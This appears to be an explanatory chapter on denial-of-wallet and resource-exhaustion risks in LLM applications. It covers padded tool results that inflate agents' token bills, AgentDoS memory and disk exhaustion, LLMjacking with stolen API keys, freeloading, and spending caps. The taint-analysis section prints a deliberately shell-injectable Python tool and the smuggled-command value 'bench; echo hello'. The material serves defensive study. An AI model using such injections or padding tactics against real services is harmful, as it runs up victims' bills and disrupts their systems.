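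In the attack that Zhang and colleagues studied, the attacker controls only the results of a tool that the victim already uses. The tool's name and description don't have to change. In a small test, they gave an agent the task of finding a report in a three-page document, and added 400 tokens of useless text to some of the results. The table shows the extra input in each later call, compared with an ordinary session:

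| Useless text added to | Call 2 | Call 3 | Call 4 |
|---|---|---|---|
| First result only | 404 | 407 | 404 |
| Every result | 404 | 812 | 1,214 |

In the first row, the victim paid three times for a single action by the attacker. When the agent's program removed the useless text before the next call, the extra input disappeared. The agent completed the task in all eight sessions, so its answers did not reveal the attack. The researchers discarded the token counts from two of those sessions because of unexplained jumps. The few remaining measurements match the growing-history formula.

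The larger experiment had 243 sessions on six model families. In most attacks, the tool returned padded text along with a reason to call it again. One version started with small results and enlarged them later, and another requested long written analyses to increase the output.

The paper reports that total input reached 14,293 times the input of a session's first call. This ratio does not compare the session with an ordinary one, and it is a poor guide to price. Any long run that starts with a short prompt has a high ratio. For example, the honest 100-call run on Opus 5.5 starts with 5,000 tokens and reads 10.4 million, a ratio of about 2,080.

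The researchers could calculate the cost of 69 attacked sessions, which averaged 82 cents and reached $3.40 at most. The most expensive of nine ordinary sessions cost 2.5 cents. But the ordinary sessions involved a different task, so the attack doesn't account for the whole difference.

When attacked and ordinary sessions both ran for four turns, the simplest attack raised the cost by only 25% with one provider and 31% with another, after cache discounts. The version that starts small cost no more than an ordinary session. Most of the harm therefore comes from persuading the agent to continue. On Llama 3.3 70B, the simplest attack failed to do so, and all nine sessions ended within two turns. The version that starts small kept the agent going for longer, and its total input averaged 386 times the first input, compared with 23 times for the simplest attack.

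An attacker needs very long sessions or very many of them to cause a large bill this way. The researchers reported the problem to several companies and projects. The maintainers of MCP's Python toolkit closed the report because they think the application should limit how much of a tool's result goes back into the prompt.

### When unchecked output causes the cost

No attacker is needed if the model itself writes something expensive and the program runs it. Suppose the shop turns `ask_database` into an agent that can run several queries and keeps their results in its prompt. The manager asks which town each product's supplier is in, and the model writes:

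```sql
SELECT products.name, suppliers.town
FROM products, suppliers
```

This query lacks the condition that matches each product to its own supplier, so the database pairs every product with every supplier. With 150 products and 200 suppliers, it returns 30,000 rows instead of 150. If each row takes 20 tokens, the result is 600,000 tokens instead of 3,000.

On Opus 5.5, reading the correct result once costs 1.2 cents and reading the faulty one costs $2.40. If the agent makes ten calls with the result in its prompt, the totals are 12 cents and $24. Perfect caching would reduce the $24 to about $4.

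The query would pass the SQL checks described earlier, because it is a single command that only reads permitted tables. The output-handling flaw is that nothing checks how much work the query causes or how large its result is.

With larger tables, a faulty query strains the database before it affects the model. If the model leaves out the same condition when joining 200,000 orders with 50,000 customers, the database has to produce 10 billion rows. The agent may never receive them, so its token bill hardly changes, but every other program that uses the database may have to wait.

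Model-written programs have the same problem. A loop without an exit will occupy a processor until something stops it, and even the parser that accepts only arithmetic doesn't prevent excessive computation. Nine to the power of nine to the power of nine is a valid expression whose answer has about 370 million digits. A sandbox that restricts only file and network access would let the calculation continue.

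The model's text can also start more model calls. If an agent hands parts of its task to three other agents, and each of those does the same, then after five levels one request has started 1 + 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 + 243 = 364 agents, each running its own loop. Safety checks can multiply calls too. *From Shield to Target* (2026) explains that many agents now have a second model review each action before it happens, and that an attacker can make that review unusually long.

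Requests can also exhaust an agent's memory or disk space, which doesn't show up on a token bill. *Autonomy Comes with Costs*, by Luo, Dai and colleagues, presented at the USENIX Security conference in 2026, describes a tool called AgentDoS that looks for such requests. It first finds the places in an agent's code that store data and works out when the agent releases that data, which may be after one reply, at the end of the conversation, or never. A model then writes ordinary-language requests that should reach those places. AgentDoS runs the requests, measures their memory or disk use, and revises them until the agent stops responding.

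The researchers tested 20 popular open-source agents and found 36 flaws in 16 of them. Fifteen of the flaws had CVE numbers by publication. Each test server had the minimum hardware its agent required, or 4 GB of memory and 10 GB of disk space if the developers hadn't specified a minimum, so a bigger server would take longer to fill.

In several cases, the agent acted on the model's output without checking how much it would have to store. One widely used agent fetched every web address the model wrote and kept all the pages in memory, even if the same address appeared a thousand times. Another saved every database query result in a history on the server. By default, it didn't send that history back to the model, so the context window didn't limit the history's growth. An attacker could repeatedly ask for a whole table until the memory was full.

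Limits on single requests didn't always help. One agent limited the number of turns in a conversation and stopped each download after 30 seconds, which the researchers estimate allowed about 300 MB. But it never deleted the files, so an attacker could start new conversations and fill a 10 GB disk with about 34 downloads. SuperAGI did delete its working folder after each conversation, but it didn't properly check file paths. An attacker could fill the disk by using file names with steps up to parent folders, the same trick that worked on Auto-GPT, to save files outside the working folder, where they remained. Because disk use builds up over many users' requests, an attacker can also stop just short of filling the disk, so that another user's next request causes the failure.

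### Accidental bills

In August 2026, Branden Jenkins, the head of the billing software company Maxio, found that one of his agents had wasted $1,000 worth of tokens in a weekend. He told Fortune that the sum was "not that much", but "pretty annoying" for one weekend (Lichtenberg, *This CEO caught his AI agent wasting $1,000 in tokens*, 2026). According to *The token wallet that refilled itself* (Churchill, 2026), the agent's prepaid account charged another $1,000 to Jenkins's card whenever the balance reached zero. This automatic refill removed the spending limit that a prepaid balance normally provides.

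An unattended agent can spend that much in a weekend without any unusual failure, because $1,000 pays for only about 24 of the uncached 100-call runs described earlier.

*One null value, 15,000 API calls, a $50,000 bill* (Churchill, 2026) describes a much larger case, drawing on coverage by the news site Help Net Security of a report by Google Cloud and its security company Mandiant. An unnamed financial company had an agent that corrected discrepancies in its accounts. The agent came to a record with a corrupted empty value, and the tool that should have formatted the record failed. The agent, which nobody had attacked, kept trying to correct the record. It made more than 15,000 paid calls in under an hour, ran up about $50,000 in cloud charges, and disrupted live transactions.

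As with the shop's broken database, a tool failed and the agent kept trying again, but the size of the bill is harder to explain. It comes to about $3.30 per call, enough for more than 800,000 input tokens on Opus 5.5, at over four calls a second. A single loop that waits for each reply could hardly run that fast with such long prompts. The agent probably made many calls at once, or the bill included other paid cloud services. If the figures are right, the agent was spending more than $800 a minute, and would have spent over $8,000 by the time an employee responded to a warning ten minutes after it was sent.

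## Stolen keys, free access and bulk copying

In the bills described so far, the victim's own program made the calls. An outsider can also call the model directly and leave the victim to pay. Providers recognise their customers by an API key, a long string of characters that a program sends with each call:

```python
def call_model(prompt):
    return post("https://models.example/reply",
                key=API_KEY, text=prompt)
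```

The provider bills the key's account. Anyone who copies `API_KEY` from the shop's code can make the same call from another computer, with any prompt. Any limits the developer has set on message length or messages per visitor are in the shop's program, which the thief never runs, so only limits set at the provider still apply.

### From cloud bills to stolen models

Denial of wallet is older than language models. Cloud companies can add servers automatically as traffic grows, so a flood of requests that would once have stopped a website may instead increase its owner's bill. The security specialist Christofer Hoff called this "economic denial of sustainability" in 2008. In 2021, Kelly, Glavin and Barrett analysed denial of wallet in serverless computing, where customers pay for each run of a small piece of code. Attackers can run up the bill for a language model in the same way, but a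 single request can cost several dollars.

Criminals had also profited from other people's cloud accounts through cryptojacking, which means using a victim's computers to mine cryptocurrency. The security company Sysdig coined "LLMjacking" for the equivalent theft of model access. In May 2024, *LLMjacking* (Brucato, 2024) described an early case. The attackers broke into a system through an old flaw in Laravel, a framework for building websites, and took its cloud credentials. They then tried to reach ten model services, intending to sell the access to other criminals. The victim would still have been billed for the usage, although the attackers, unlike someone who floods a website to ruin its owner, had no particular interest in causing losses.

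At first, such attackers used models that the victim had already switched on. Later in 2024, according to CyberInsider, Sysdig found them switching on models themselves. Amazon's model service, Bedrock, received more than 85,000 of their requests on 11 July alone. Sysdig estimated that attackers using Claude 3 Opus, then one of the most expensive models, could cost a victim over $100,000 a day.

### Bills and resale in 2026

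Google's *The Rise of LLMJacking* (2026), published in November, covers break-ins that Mandiant investigated. Muncaster (2026), in *LLMJacking is Costing Some Businesses Up to $1m*, reports that fraudulent charges exceeded $100,000 in a single day in some cases and reached $1 million at some organisations before they cut off access. Sugue (2026), in *Cybercriminals hijack LLM access, racking up bills*, reports that several victims had never used the model services that the attackers switched on. One attacker created and deleted short-lived accounts while watching the cloud provider's billing page to see how much the victim owed.

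Some groups steal access and others sell it. The sellers run what Google calls "LLM mixers", which pool stolen keys and pass customers' requests through them. *Someone will pay $60 a month for your AI key* (Heaton, 2026) describes one called Jet Night, which sells "unlimited" use of leading models for about $60 a month. An attacker supplying it made more than 500,000 calls in under eight hours. A service of this kind ran up almost $1 million in charges for one victim. At Jet Night's price, more than 16,000 customers would have to pay for a month to cover that sum, so the price makes sense only if the seller doesn't pay for the models.

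Thieves can find a leaked key quickly. Heaton reports an experiment in which researchers at Stony Brook University hid working keys in 300 decoy software packages and published them without advertising them. A bot tested an Amazon cloud key 7.86 seconds after publication. The OpenAI keys went unused for weeks, and then someone spent the whole balance in under 24 hours. The researchers think that thieves check keys, resell them and hold them until a buyer needs them. A month without activity after a leak is therefore poor evidence that nobody has the key. The owner has to cancel a leaked key, because deleting it from the code leaves copies in the code's history.

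Some victims had published their keys on purpose. Google's guidance allowed developers to put keys for services such as Maps in the public code of their websites. TechRadar reports that, according to the security company CloudSek, some of these keys later gained access to Google's Gemini models. *Unrestricted API key + AI Studio silently enabled Gemini*, a post on Google's developer forum by the person who runs a Brazilian tyre shop's website, describes one such case. The site had used an unrestricted Maps key since 2021. In late 2025, its owner approved the use of Gemini for a small internal program, which gave every unrestricted key in the project access to Gemini as well. The shop's usual bill was $44 a month, but on 10 June 2026 Google charged it $7,500 within an hour, with another $6,500 pending.

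It is hard to call this careless, because the key could do little harm when the owner published it, and the post says that Google's approval screen gave no warning of the change. A startup of three developers in Mexico had a larger bill. Techzine reports that someone used the startup's key to run up $82,314 in two days in February 2026, about 38 years of its usual spending with Google. This figure also comes from the victim. At the time of Maruccia's *A stolen Gemini API key turned a $180 bill into $82,000*, the developers said that Google had not offered to reduce the bill.

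Microsoft has sued alleged resellers. Its complaint, filed in Virginia in December 2024, accuses ten people of using stolen keys and custom software to get into its Azure OpenAI service. The complaint invokes laws on computer fraud, copyright, trademarks and organised crime, according to CyberScoop's *Microsoft moves to disrupt hacking-as-a-service scheme that’s bypassing AI safety measures*. A judge allowed Microsoft to seize a website that it said was central to the scheme, according to Law360's *Microsoft Corporation v. Does 4-10 Operating an Azure Abuse Network* (2024).

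Microsoft said in *Disrupting a global cybercrime network abusing generative AI* (2025) that the group had altered the services and resold access, with instructions for making sexual images of celebrities. In a proposed amended complaint, Microsoft alleges that one defendant also used what appeared to be stolen Google keys. These are allegations, but they point to a harm beyond the bill, since a stolen key can link its owner's account to abusive material.

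### Model servers without a login

A company that runs an open model on its own hardware may have no key to steal, because its server doesn't require one. Elzer, Johansen and Vasilomanolakis (2026), in *OllamaDrama*, set up a decoy model server to see what attackers would do. Attackers used the model without logging in and downloaded others onto the server, including versions altered to remove their refusals. Some flooded the server with tokens or requested endless replies. Others tried to install cryptocurrency-mining software, or to use server-side request forgery to get cloud credentials, which can give an attacker access to an account whose bill has no fixed limit.

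Criminals also resell this access. Techzine reports that decoys recorded 35,000 attack sessions between December 2025 and January 2026, an average of 972 a day. Pillar Security, which discovered the campaign, found an organised supply chain for locating exposed model and MCP servers, checking that they worked and selling access to them. Attacks on decoys show how actively criminals are looking for servers, but don't measure how many real ones they have used.

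### Free products turned into general-purpose models

A visitor can use the shop's chat box as a free language model without breaking in. If the visitor asks it to write a computer program instead of asking it to find a bench, the model may well write one, and the shop pays for the tokens. A project called Chipotlai Max turned the restaurant chain Chipotle's customer-support chatbot into a free model for coding assistants.

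In *Demystifying Real-world LLM Service Freeloading*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) looked for software that does this systematically. They define freeloading as taking free access meant for a product's own website or program and offering it through a separate API, against the provider's terms. They exclude paid subscriptions, models that people run themselves, and attacks meant only to exhaust a service.

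The researchers searched the code-sharing site GitHub and found 5,032 candidate projects. They narrowed these down with code analysis and a coding agent, and then checked every project they kept. The result was 513 projects drawing on 64 services, through 1,588 separate paths from a project's API to a service:

| How the project reaches the model | Paths |
|---|---|
| Its own code imitates the requests that the official website or program sends | 1,322 |
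| It controls the website in a browser, or sends requests from inside the browser session | 228 |
| It passes the prompt to the provider's official program | 38 |

The project usually has to translate between formats as well. A coding assistant sends a list of earlier messages and may need a tool call in return, whereas a chat website accepts typed text and displays text. On half of the paths, the project rebuilt the prompt or conversation history to suit the product. On 210 paths, it turned the model's ordinary text into something that looked like a tool call.

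The Aurora project uses ChatGPT's anonymous free access, so its users don't need an account. Antigravity-Tools-LS draws on a pool of free accounts for Google's coding product Antigravity. For each request, it picks the first active account with allowance left for the chosen model. Every account can stay within its own limit while the pool uses far more than one person's share. The study found account selection or rotation on 304 paths (19.1%).

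DeepSeek's website was the most common source, with 105 projects, followed by Gemini's (86), Qwen's (57) and ChatGPT's (37). Of the 513 projects, 477 dated from 2026, and developers created 253 of them between August and October. The median project had one star, GitHub's equivalent of a bookmark, while the ten most popular had 89% of all the stars. The study counted projects but didn't measure their use, so it can't show how many tokens they consumed or what they cost the providers.

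Hou and colleagues could read the terms of 62 services, and 58 explicitly prohibited at least one of these practices. Counting partial restrictions, 57 services restricted automated access, 50 restricted passing the service on to others, and 35 restricted multiple accounts or repeated claims of free offers. The researchers notified all 64 services and reported the projects to GitHub, which had already put malicious-content warnings on two of the projects. Their paper includes no replies from the providers. They recommend that providers check eligibility each time the model runs, limit the reuse of login data and look for accounts that act together.

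The category covers conduct that varies widely in seriousness. Someone who uses one free account through an unofficial program and stays within the account's allowance costs the provider about as much as someone who types the same questions into the website. Reselling is harder to defend. The study cites a report that attackers created thousands of accounts at Kilo Code, a coding service, to collect free credits, then sold the accounts or access to models through them.

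### Copying a model through its answers

A customer can also imitate a model by sending it many prompts, saving the replies, and training another model to produce similar ones. OWASP calls this functional model replication and cites Alpaca as an example. To make Alpaca in 2023, Stanford researchers collected 52,000 examples from an OpenAI model for less than $500 and used them to train a small Meta model to follow instructions.

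Some services also return the probabilities the model assigned to possible next tokens. Someone copying the model can learn more from these probabilities than from the chosen words, and in 2024 researchers used them to recover the final layer of two small OpenAI models for under $20. OWASP therefore advises providers to restrict access to the probabilities. Copying still takes many calls, which is why OWASP classes it as unbounded consumption.

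In February 2026, Anthropic accused three Chinese AI companies, DeepSeek, Moonshot and MiniMax, of copying Claude's abilities this way. It said they had used about 24,000 fraudulent accounts for more than 16 million exchanges, partly through services that resell access to Claude. That averages fewer than 700 exchanges per account, which might not look unusual for a business customer.

People disagree about whether this copying is ethical and how much it helps. Training one model on another's answers is a common technique, and Anthropic accepts that it is legitimate when, for example, a company makes a smaller version of its own model. It objected to competitors doing so against its terms and under false identities. Critics replied that Anthropic had built its own models on other people's writing, and in 2025 it had agreed to pay $1.5 billion to settle a lawsuit over pirated books. The criticism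 somewhat weakens the case for calling the copying theft, but it doesn't excuse the false accounts. No one can tell from the number of exchanges how much the three companies' models improved. Anthropic attributed only about 150,000 of them to DeepSeek, roughly three times the number of examples used to train Alpaca, a far smaller model.

A spending limit wouldn't have prevented this. If each of the 16 million replies were 1,000 tokens long, the output would cost $320,000 at the current price of Claude Opus 5.5. A large AI company could pay that in full. The provider would have no unpaid bill and perhaps no slowdown, but it would still have lost some of its advantage over a competitor.

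A limit does help against a stolen key, though it can move the harm from the shop to its customers. If the shop caps its spending at $50 a day, a thief can't cost it more than that, but once the $50 is gone, the chat box stops answering questions about benches. On an open server that the shop owns, the main harm is that other users lose processing time.

To stop copying, a provider has to distinguish it from the requests of paying customers, some of whom have legitimate reasons to send millions of prompts. A low limit on each account would obstruct those customers, and a copier could get around it by opening more accounts. OWASP also suggests watermarking, which adds a detectable pattern to the model's output. This might help a provider prove later that a competitor trained on its answers, but it doesn't prevent the copying.

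## Limiting use, time and spending

Usage limits rarely stop a patient person from copying a model, but they can prevent very large bills if they cap tokens rather than just requests. If a service lets each customer send 60 requests a minute and every reply is 100,000 tokens long, a customer can generate 360 million tokens an hour without exceeding the limit. At an illustrative price of $15 per million output tokens, that costs $5,400. Limiting each customer to 200,000 output tokens a minute instead would cap the hourly total at 12 million tokens, which cost $180.

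A token limit restricts only the rate of spending. At $180 an hour, a month-long attack would still cost about $130,000, so customers also need a limit on total spending.

Anthropic's *Rate limits* shows how rate limits and spending caps work together. On the lowest standard tier, a customer of Claude Opus 5.5 can send 4,000 requests, 2 million input tokens and 400,000 output tokens a minute. A customer who used both token limits in full would spend $16 a minute and reach the tier's monthly spending cap of $500 in about half an hour. Text that the model reads from the cache doesn't count towards the input limit, but the customer still pays for it.

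### The controls in the order a request meets them

Here is the shop's chat program with limits added:

```python
def handle(message, user):
    if len(message) > 2000:
        return "Please ask a shorter question."
    prompt = RULES + help_pages(message) + message
    for step in range(5):
        quote = highest_cost(prompt, max_output=500)
        if not reserve(user, quote):
            return "Please try again tomorrow."
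        reply = call_model(prompt, max_output=500, timeout=30)
        settle(user, quote, reply.cost)
        if not reply.tool_call:
            return reply.text
        prompt = prompt + reply.text + run_tool(reply.tool_call)
    return "Please email the shop."
```

The program must first identify `user`, because every per-user limit depends on it. A login is the best evidence. Without one, the shop can use a browser cookie, which a visitor can delete, or a network address, which a whole office may share. Free accounts are weak evidence too, since one person can open many.

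The length check stops a visitor from pasting in a book-length text. It doesn't cover the help pages and tool results that the program adds later, and it doesn't stop short questions that produce long answers. ThinkTrap's inputs, for example, were only 20 tokens long.

The program can calculate the maximum cost of a call in advance, but not the actual cost. The first call about the bench has 3,000 input tokens and may produce up to 500 output tokens, so the quote on Opus 5.5 is 2.2 cents. `reserve` takes this from the user's budget before the call. The reply is only 50 tokens long, so the call costs 1.3 cents and `settle` returns the other 0.9. The program reserves the money because requests can arrive together. If it checked only past spending, a hundred simultaneous requests could all pass because of the same unspent cent.

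*Bounded Autonomy* (Chen, Lyu and colleagues, 2026) uses this method to control agents. If a call ends without a clear result, the system keeps the money reserved until it can establish the cost. But a generous output limit ties up a lot of money. On GPT-6.2 Astra, a call that may produce 128,000 tokens reserves more than $5, even if the answer is one sentence.

The output limit prevents a single enormous reply, but not a long series of moderate ones like those Zhou and colleagues' malicious tool produced. If the limit includes reasoning tokens, the model may also reach it before writing any of the answer. Anthropic points out that a high output limit doesn't use up a customer's rate limit, which counts only the tokens the model writes. But it does raise the maximum cost of each call.

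A timeout spares the customer a long wait, but the shop may still have to pay for the call. Microsoft charges for requests that its service has processed, even if they end in a timeout error. Google's *Billing* says Gemini requests that fail with a 400 or 500 error are not charged, though they still count towards quota. If a program retries after every timeout, the shop may pay for the same work several times.

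The limit of five steps ends the loop when the order database is down. But a step count is a poor guide to cost. Chen and colleagues allow 100 model calls per task, and the uncached run of 100 calls described earlier costs $41.60. A single tool result can be huge, as with the faulty supplier query, so tools need limits on the size of their results as well as on running time. Chen and colleagues stop each tool call after two minutes and the whole task after 35 minutes.

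A budget for each user covers all of that person's requests, whatever made them expensive. It doesn't limit the number of users, so a thousand accounts with $1 each can spend $1,000. An overall spending cap limits that total, and if the provider enforces it, it also covers requests made with a stolen API key. But when spending reaches the cap, the service stops for everyone.

### Fair shares of a busy server

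For a company that runs its own model, the scarce resource is server capacity. Fixed limits can waste it, because a customer who has used up an allowance has to wait even when the server is idle. *Fairness in Serving Large Language Models* (Sheng, Cao and colleagues, 2024) proposed a scheduler, the Virtual Token Counter, that limits customers only when others are waiting.

The server keeps a running total of each customer's tokens, counting an output token twice as much as an input token. When it has room for another request, it chooses the waiting customer with the lowest total. If one customer's requests use 2,000 tokens each and another's use 200, the second customer has about ten requests served for each of the first customer's. The server adds output tokens to the totals as the model writes them, so it doesn't have to predict the length of a reply.

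Customers can't save up unused time. When a customer returns after a break, the server raises their total to at least the lowest total among customers already waiting. Otherwise a customer who had been away for a day could monopolise the server.

Sheng and colleagues proved that two customers who always have requests waiting receive nearly equal service. The difference between them never exceeds

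2 × max(input weight × longest input, output weight × tokens that fit in memory)

On their main test server, which had room for 10,000 tokens, this comes to 40,000 units, equivalent to 20,000 output tokens. The bound does not change over time.

They also replayed real chatbot traffic as if it came from 27 customers. A limit of five requests a minute kept waits short, but the server processed only 340 tokens a second, compared with 779 under the Virtual Token Counter. Raising the limit to 30 recovered most of the speed but let the heaviest users delay everyone else again. Under the Virtual Token Counter, only customers who asked for more than their share waited much longer.

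This scheduler doesn't interrupt running requests, so when long replies fill the memory, they stay there until they finish. It also divides the server among accounts, so an attacker with ten accounts gets ten shares. *Equinox* (2025) objects that no single measure covers everything fairness requires. For instance, two customers with equal token totals can take up very different amounts of memory. *Equinox* therefore keeps separate counters for fairness to users and fair use of resources, and uses predictions to balance them.

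### Hard caps and alerts

A spending alert sends a message, while a hard cap makes the provider refuse further requests. OpenAI's *Spend limits* and Mistral AI's *Usage limits* describe hard caps that customers can set, and Anthropic and Google offer them too. Google Cloud's *Manage spend cap budgets* describes caps for Gemini and three other services.

AWS re:Post's *Governing Amazon Bedrock costs* explains how customers of Bedrock, Amazon's model service, can build a hard stop on spending from budgets and their own automation. Microsoft (2024) described a similar arrangement for its Azure cloud.

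| Service | What happens at the limit | Delay that the provider mentions |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | Alerts only notify; an optional hard limit rejects requests | Not instantaneous, no figure |
| Anthropic | The tier's cap, or a lower limit set by the customer, rejects requests | None |
| Google, Gemini API | Project and account caps pause the service | Up to about 10 minutes |
| Google Cloud | The customer chooses between alerts and a cap | Not instantaneous; actual costs can take over 24 hours to appear |
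| Mistral AI | A workspace's cap rejects requests | None |
| AWS Budgets | Alerts, plus any action the customer has set up | Updates typically 8 to 12 hours apart |
| Microsoft Azure | Alerts, plus any action the customer has set up | Some delay, no figure |

A provider can change whether a spending cap blocks requests or only sends an alert. Willison (2024) welcomed OpenAI's new project caps in May 2024 because they let a developer publish an odd demo without risking "accidental bankruptcy". OpenAI later turned these caps into alerts. The OpenAI forum thread *How to Set Billing Limits and Restrict Model Usage for a Project* quotes the new wording, under which requests over the budget would continue "without interruption". Hard limits returned on 22 July 2026, according to Torii's *Google shipped hard monthly spend caps for AI agents*.

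Caps also have exceptions. Anthropic warns that the limit on a customer's default workspace may not count some usage, including managed agent sessions, although the organisation-wide limit does. At Google, batch jobs and agent sessions can run past a project's cap, and a prepaid balance can fall below zero. If a Google Cloud customer manually lifts a cap after it takes effect, the cap won't take effect again that month unless the customer also raises the amount.

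Most of these caps are monthly, so an attacker can use up the whole month's budget on the first day. Anthropic also has an interface for setting daily and weekly limits.

### How much a delay can cost

The amount that someone can spend after reaching a cap is roughly

spending per minute × minutes of delay

plus the cost of requests that are still running. The table applies this to the two limits at the start of this section and to the Brazilian tyre shop whose key cost it $7,500 in an hour:

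| Spending rate | In 10 minutes | In 12 hours |
|---|---|---|
| $3 a minute (200,000 output tokens) | $30 | $2,160 |
| $90 a minute (60 very long replies) | $900 | $64,800 |
| $125 a minute (the tyre shop) | $1,250 | $90,000 |

A ten-minute delay is tolerable for most businesses, but a budget that updates every 12 hours does little against a fast attack, even if the customer has automated the response. Google Cloud makes customers pay for any spending above the cap and advises them to set it slightly below what they can afford. Customers with a rate limit can calculate how far below to set it. If the furniture shop can afford $500 and can't spend more than $3 a minute, a cap of $470 leaves enough for a ten-minute delay.

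Late billing figures also make it hard to tell whether an attack has ended. PPC Land's *Google finally adds Gemini API spend caps after billing chaos hit devs* mentions a developer who saw charges grow by $200 in 20 minutes after deleting every key. Some or all of that increase may have come from earlier use that had only just reached the bill. The shop's own program can count token use sooner, because model services normally report it with each reply, but that count leaves out a thief's use of the key.

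### Tests of limits on agents

Zhang and colleagues, who studied padded tool results, also tested a defence against them. Before each model call, the defence checks the size of the prompt, its growth since the last call, the number of tool calls and the cost so far. At the middle of three settings, the conditions that stop a session include prompt growth of more than 10,000 tokens in one step and a cost above 10 cents.

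The researchers replayed 41 recorded attacks, and the defence stopped all of them at every setting. Recorded attacks can't adapt to a defence, so the researchers also built seven sequences, most of them designed to avoid the growth alarm. The other limits caught those, and none cost more than 10.5 cents. In live tests, the defence stopped 23 of 25 attacks, and a provider's own size limit blocked the other two.

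The growth alarm stopped only 2 of 1,050 legitimate sessions, but the limit of five tool-using turns in a row interrupted all 60 legitimate workflows that needed 8 to 12 steps. When the researchers made this limit depend on how fast the stored history was growing, it interrupted none of the 60, and the defence as a whole still stopped every recorded attack. The 10-cent cap still stopped seven of the workflows.

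In a separate test of the cost cap alone, 13 of 24 long workflows finished and the cap stopped nine, each with nine of its ten stages complete. The average session cost 9.9 cents. Another version raised the cap to 13 and then 16 cents as independent checks confirmed progress. With that version, 22 workflows finished and the cap stopped none, at an average cost of 11.3 cents. The researchers acknowledge that the larger budget may explain the improvement, since they didn't test a fixed cap of 16 cents. The lower cap saved little because most of the money had been spent by the time it stopped a job.

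In Chen and colleagues' design, a trusted program divides a task into fixed subtasks and gives each one a token allowance based on the most demanding honest runs. Retrying a subtask doesn't renew its allowance. When the agent finishes a subtask, the program checks the result in the business's own records and replaces the conversation so far with a short summary. It also reserves a tenth of the total budget for up to three attempts by the agent to recover from an interruption.

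They tested this on 127 simulated tasks, mostly in customer service, against an agent that had the same subtasks but not the new controls. These are the results with Alibaba's Qwen3.8-Flash at the highest strength of each attack:

| Attack | Tokens without the controls | Tokens with them | Effect on tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 179,400 | 179,800 | None (76%) |
| Padding after up to four tool calls | 274,700 | 212,800 | Down from 57% to 43% |
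| One very long tool result | 912,800 | about 211,000 | Down 3 points |
| Up to four false timeouts | 218,300 | 207,200 | Up from 43% to 48% |

The defence saved 77% of the tokens when a tool returned one very long result, but only 5% under false timeouts, which hadn't raised the total much. Completion of ordinary tasks stayed at 76% overall, but it fell from 69% to 64% on retail tasks and from 87% to 84% on telecoms tasks, and rose on airline and banking tasks. These differences amount to one or two tasks each, so they could easily be due to chance.

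Holding back money for recovery raised the share of tasks the agent completed under the three attacks from 21–31% to 55–64%. A strict budget alone would have limited spending, but the attacks would still have kept the agent from finishing most of its tasks.

The design suits jobs such as refunds, which a developer can divide into subtasks in advance and confirm as complete in a database. An agent doing open-ended research has no fixed list of subtasks and often no record that shows when it has finished.

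### Failures that limits cause

An attacker can use up a limit that customers share. An attack that costs $3 a minute would reach a $500 monthly cap in less than three hours, and the shop's chat box could then be off for the rest of the month. Other programs may stop too. For example, when a prepaid Google account's balance reaches zero, every key in every linked project stops working. The shop can reduce this risk by giving the chat box its own project with a lower cap and limiting each visitor to a small share of that cap.

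A sudden rush of honest customers, perhaps after a television appearance, can cause the same trouble. Anthropic limits how quickly an organisation's use can grow, so it could refuse requests even if the shop was below its other limits.

The program then has to interpret the refusal correctly. Anthropic uses the same error type for a per-minute rate limit and for a tier's monthly cap. The program can recognize the monthly cap only by the detailed error code and the absence of a waiting time. In that case, retries will fail until the next month, unless Anthropic raises the cap sooner.

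An output limit can also damage the reply itself. Suppose the model reaches its limit in the middle of a tool call:

```json
{"tool": "find_order", "product": "ben
```

This isn't valid JSON, so a schema check will reject it. If the program retries with the same limit, the next reply may break off too, and the shop pays for every attempt.

A reply that is still valid after the cut is more dangerous. Suppose an agent that tidies the shop's database writes this command to delete old shopping baskets:

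```sql
DELETE FROM baskets WHERE updated < '2026-01-01'
```

If the reply ends after `baskets`, the database receives a complete command that deletes every basket. Model services normally report whether a reply ended naturally or reached its limit, so before any other check, the program should discard a command that was cut off. Chen and colleagues' system similarly rejects overlong summaries between subtasks, or handles them as exceptions, because shortening them could remove a permission or an unfinished duty.

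OWASP recommends that an application keep some functions working when it is overloaded. When the shop's budget runs out, the page could replace the chat box with an ordinary form where the customer can enter an order number and get the bench's delivery date without using a model.

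## How the flaws are found and how common they are

Missing checks are hard to notice in a program with dozens of tools, so researchers have built software that searches for them. The software's results, public vulnerability records and OWASP's incident data give some idea of how common the two flaws are, although each source counts something different.

### Following untrusted text through a program

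Taint analysis looks for injection flaws by reading code without running it. The analyser marks text from outside as tainted, follows it through the program and raises an alert if it reaches a sink. Suppose the shop's model can use this tool:

```python
def find_product(name):
    command = "lookup " + name
    return subprocess.run(command, shell=True)
```

The analyser marks `name`, and it also marks `command` because `command` contains `name`. The last line passes `command` to a shell, so the analyser raises an alert. If the developer first passed `name` through `shlex.quote`, a Python function that escapes text for the shell, the analyser would remove the mark. Such a sanitiser works for only one kind of sink, so the same `name` should still cause an alert if it also reaches a database query.

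A model in the middle breaks the trace:

```python
reply = call_model(RULES + message)
run_tool(reply.tool_call)
```

The analyser can follow the customer's message as far as `call_model`, which sends it to the provider. The reply comes back as new text, and no line of code connects its words to those of the message. If the analyser drops the mark here, it misses every attack that goes through the model. If it marks every reply, it catches those attacks but also reports paths that no real prompt could make the model follow.

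The trace breaks again at `run_tool`, which picks a function by the name in the model's reply, so the code has no fixed path from the chat box to `find_product`.

VIPER-MCP, the tool that Sun and colleagues used to scan MCP servers, avoids both breaks by starting its analysis after the model. It marks every tool's arguments as tainted, whoever wrote them, and looks for paths from them to functions that run shell commands, fetch URLs or open files. The first alerts give only a location in a file, so a second pass finds the smallest function that encloses that location and identifies the tool it belongs to.

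An alert doesn't prove that an attacker can exploit the code path. Bytebot, the desktop agent whose file-writing tool had a command-injection flaw, offers 16 tools with overlapping purposes, so a request aimed at the flawed tool may trigger a harmless one instead. The model may also refuse a suspicious file path or clean it up before passing it on.

### Confirming a path with trial inputs

Fuzzing means running a program on many automatically generated inputs and watching what happens. For an image viewer, the inputs might be damaged picture files, and a crash would reveal a flaw. For an agent, the inputs are sentences, and the tester watches whether text from them reaches the sink in a harmful form. At the shop, a tester could ask the chat box for a product named `bench; echo hello` and check whether the server prints "hello". If the model passes on only "bench", the tester learns nothing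 about `find_product` and has to reword the request.

VIPER-MCP automates this rewording. A model writes several requests for each suspected path, and an agent carries them out on a server that records every call to a sink. VIPER-MCP scores each attempt by how far it got and revises the better ones. It changes the request if the agent chose the wrong tool, or the value if the agent chose the right tool but something blocked or altered the value. A separate component then checks whether the recorded evidence shows a real attack.

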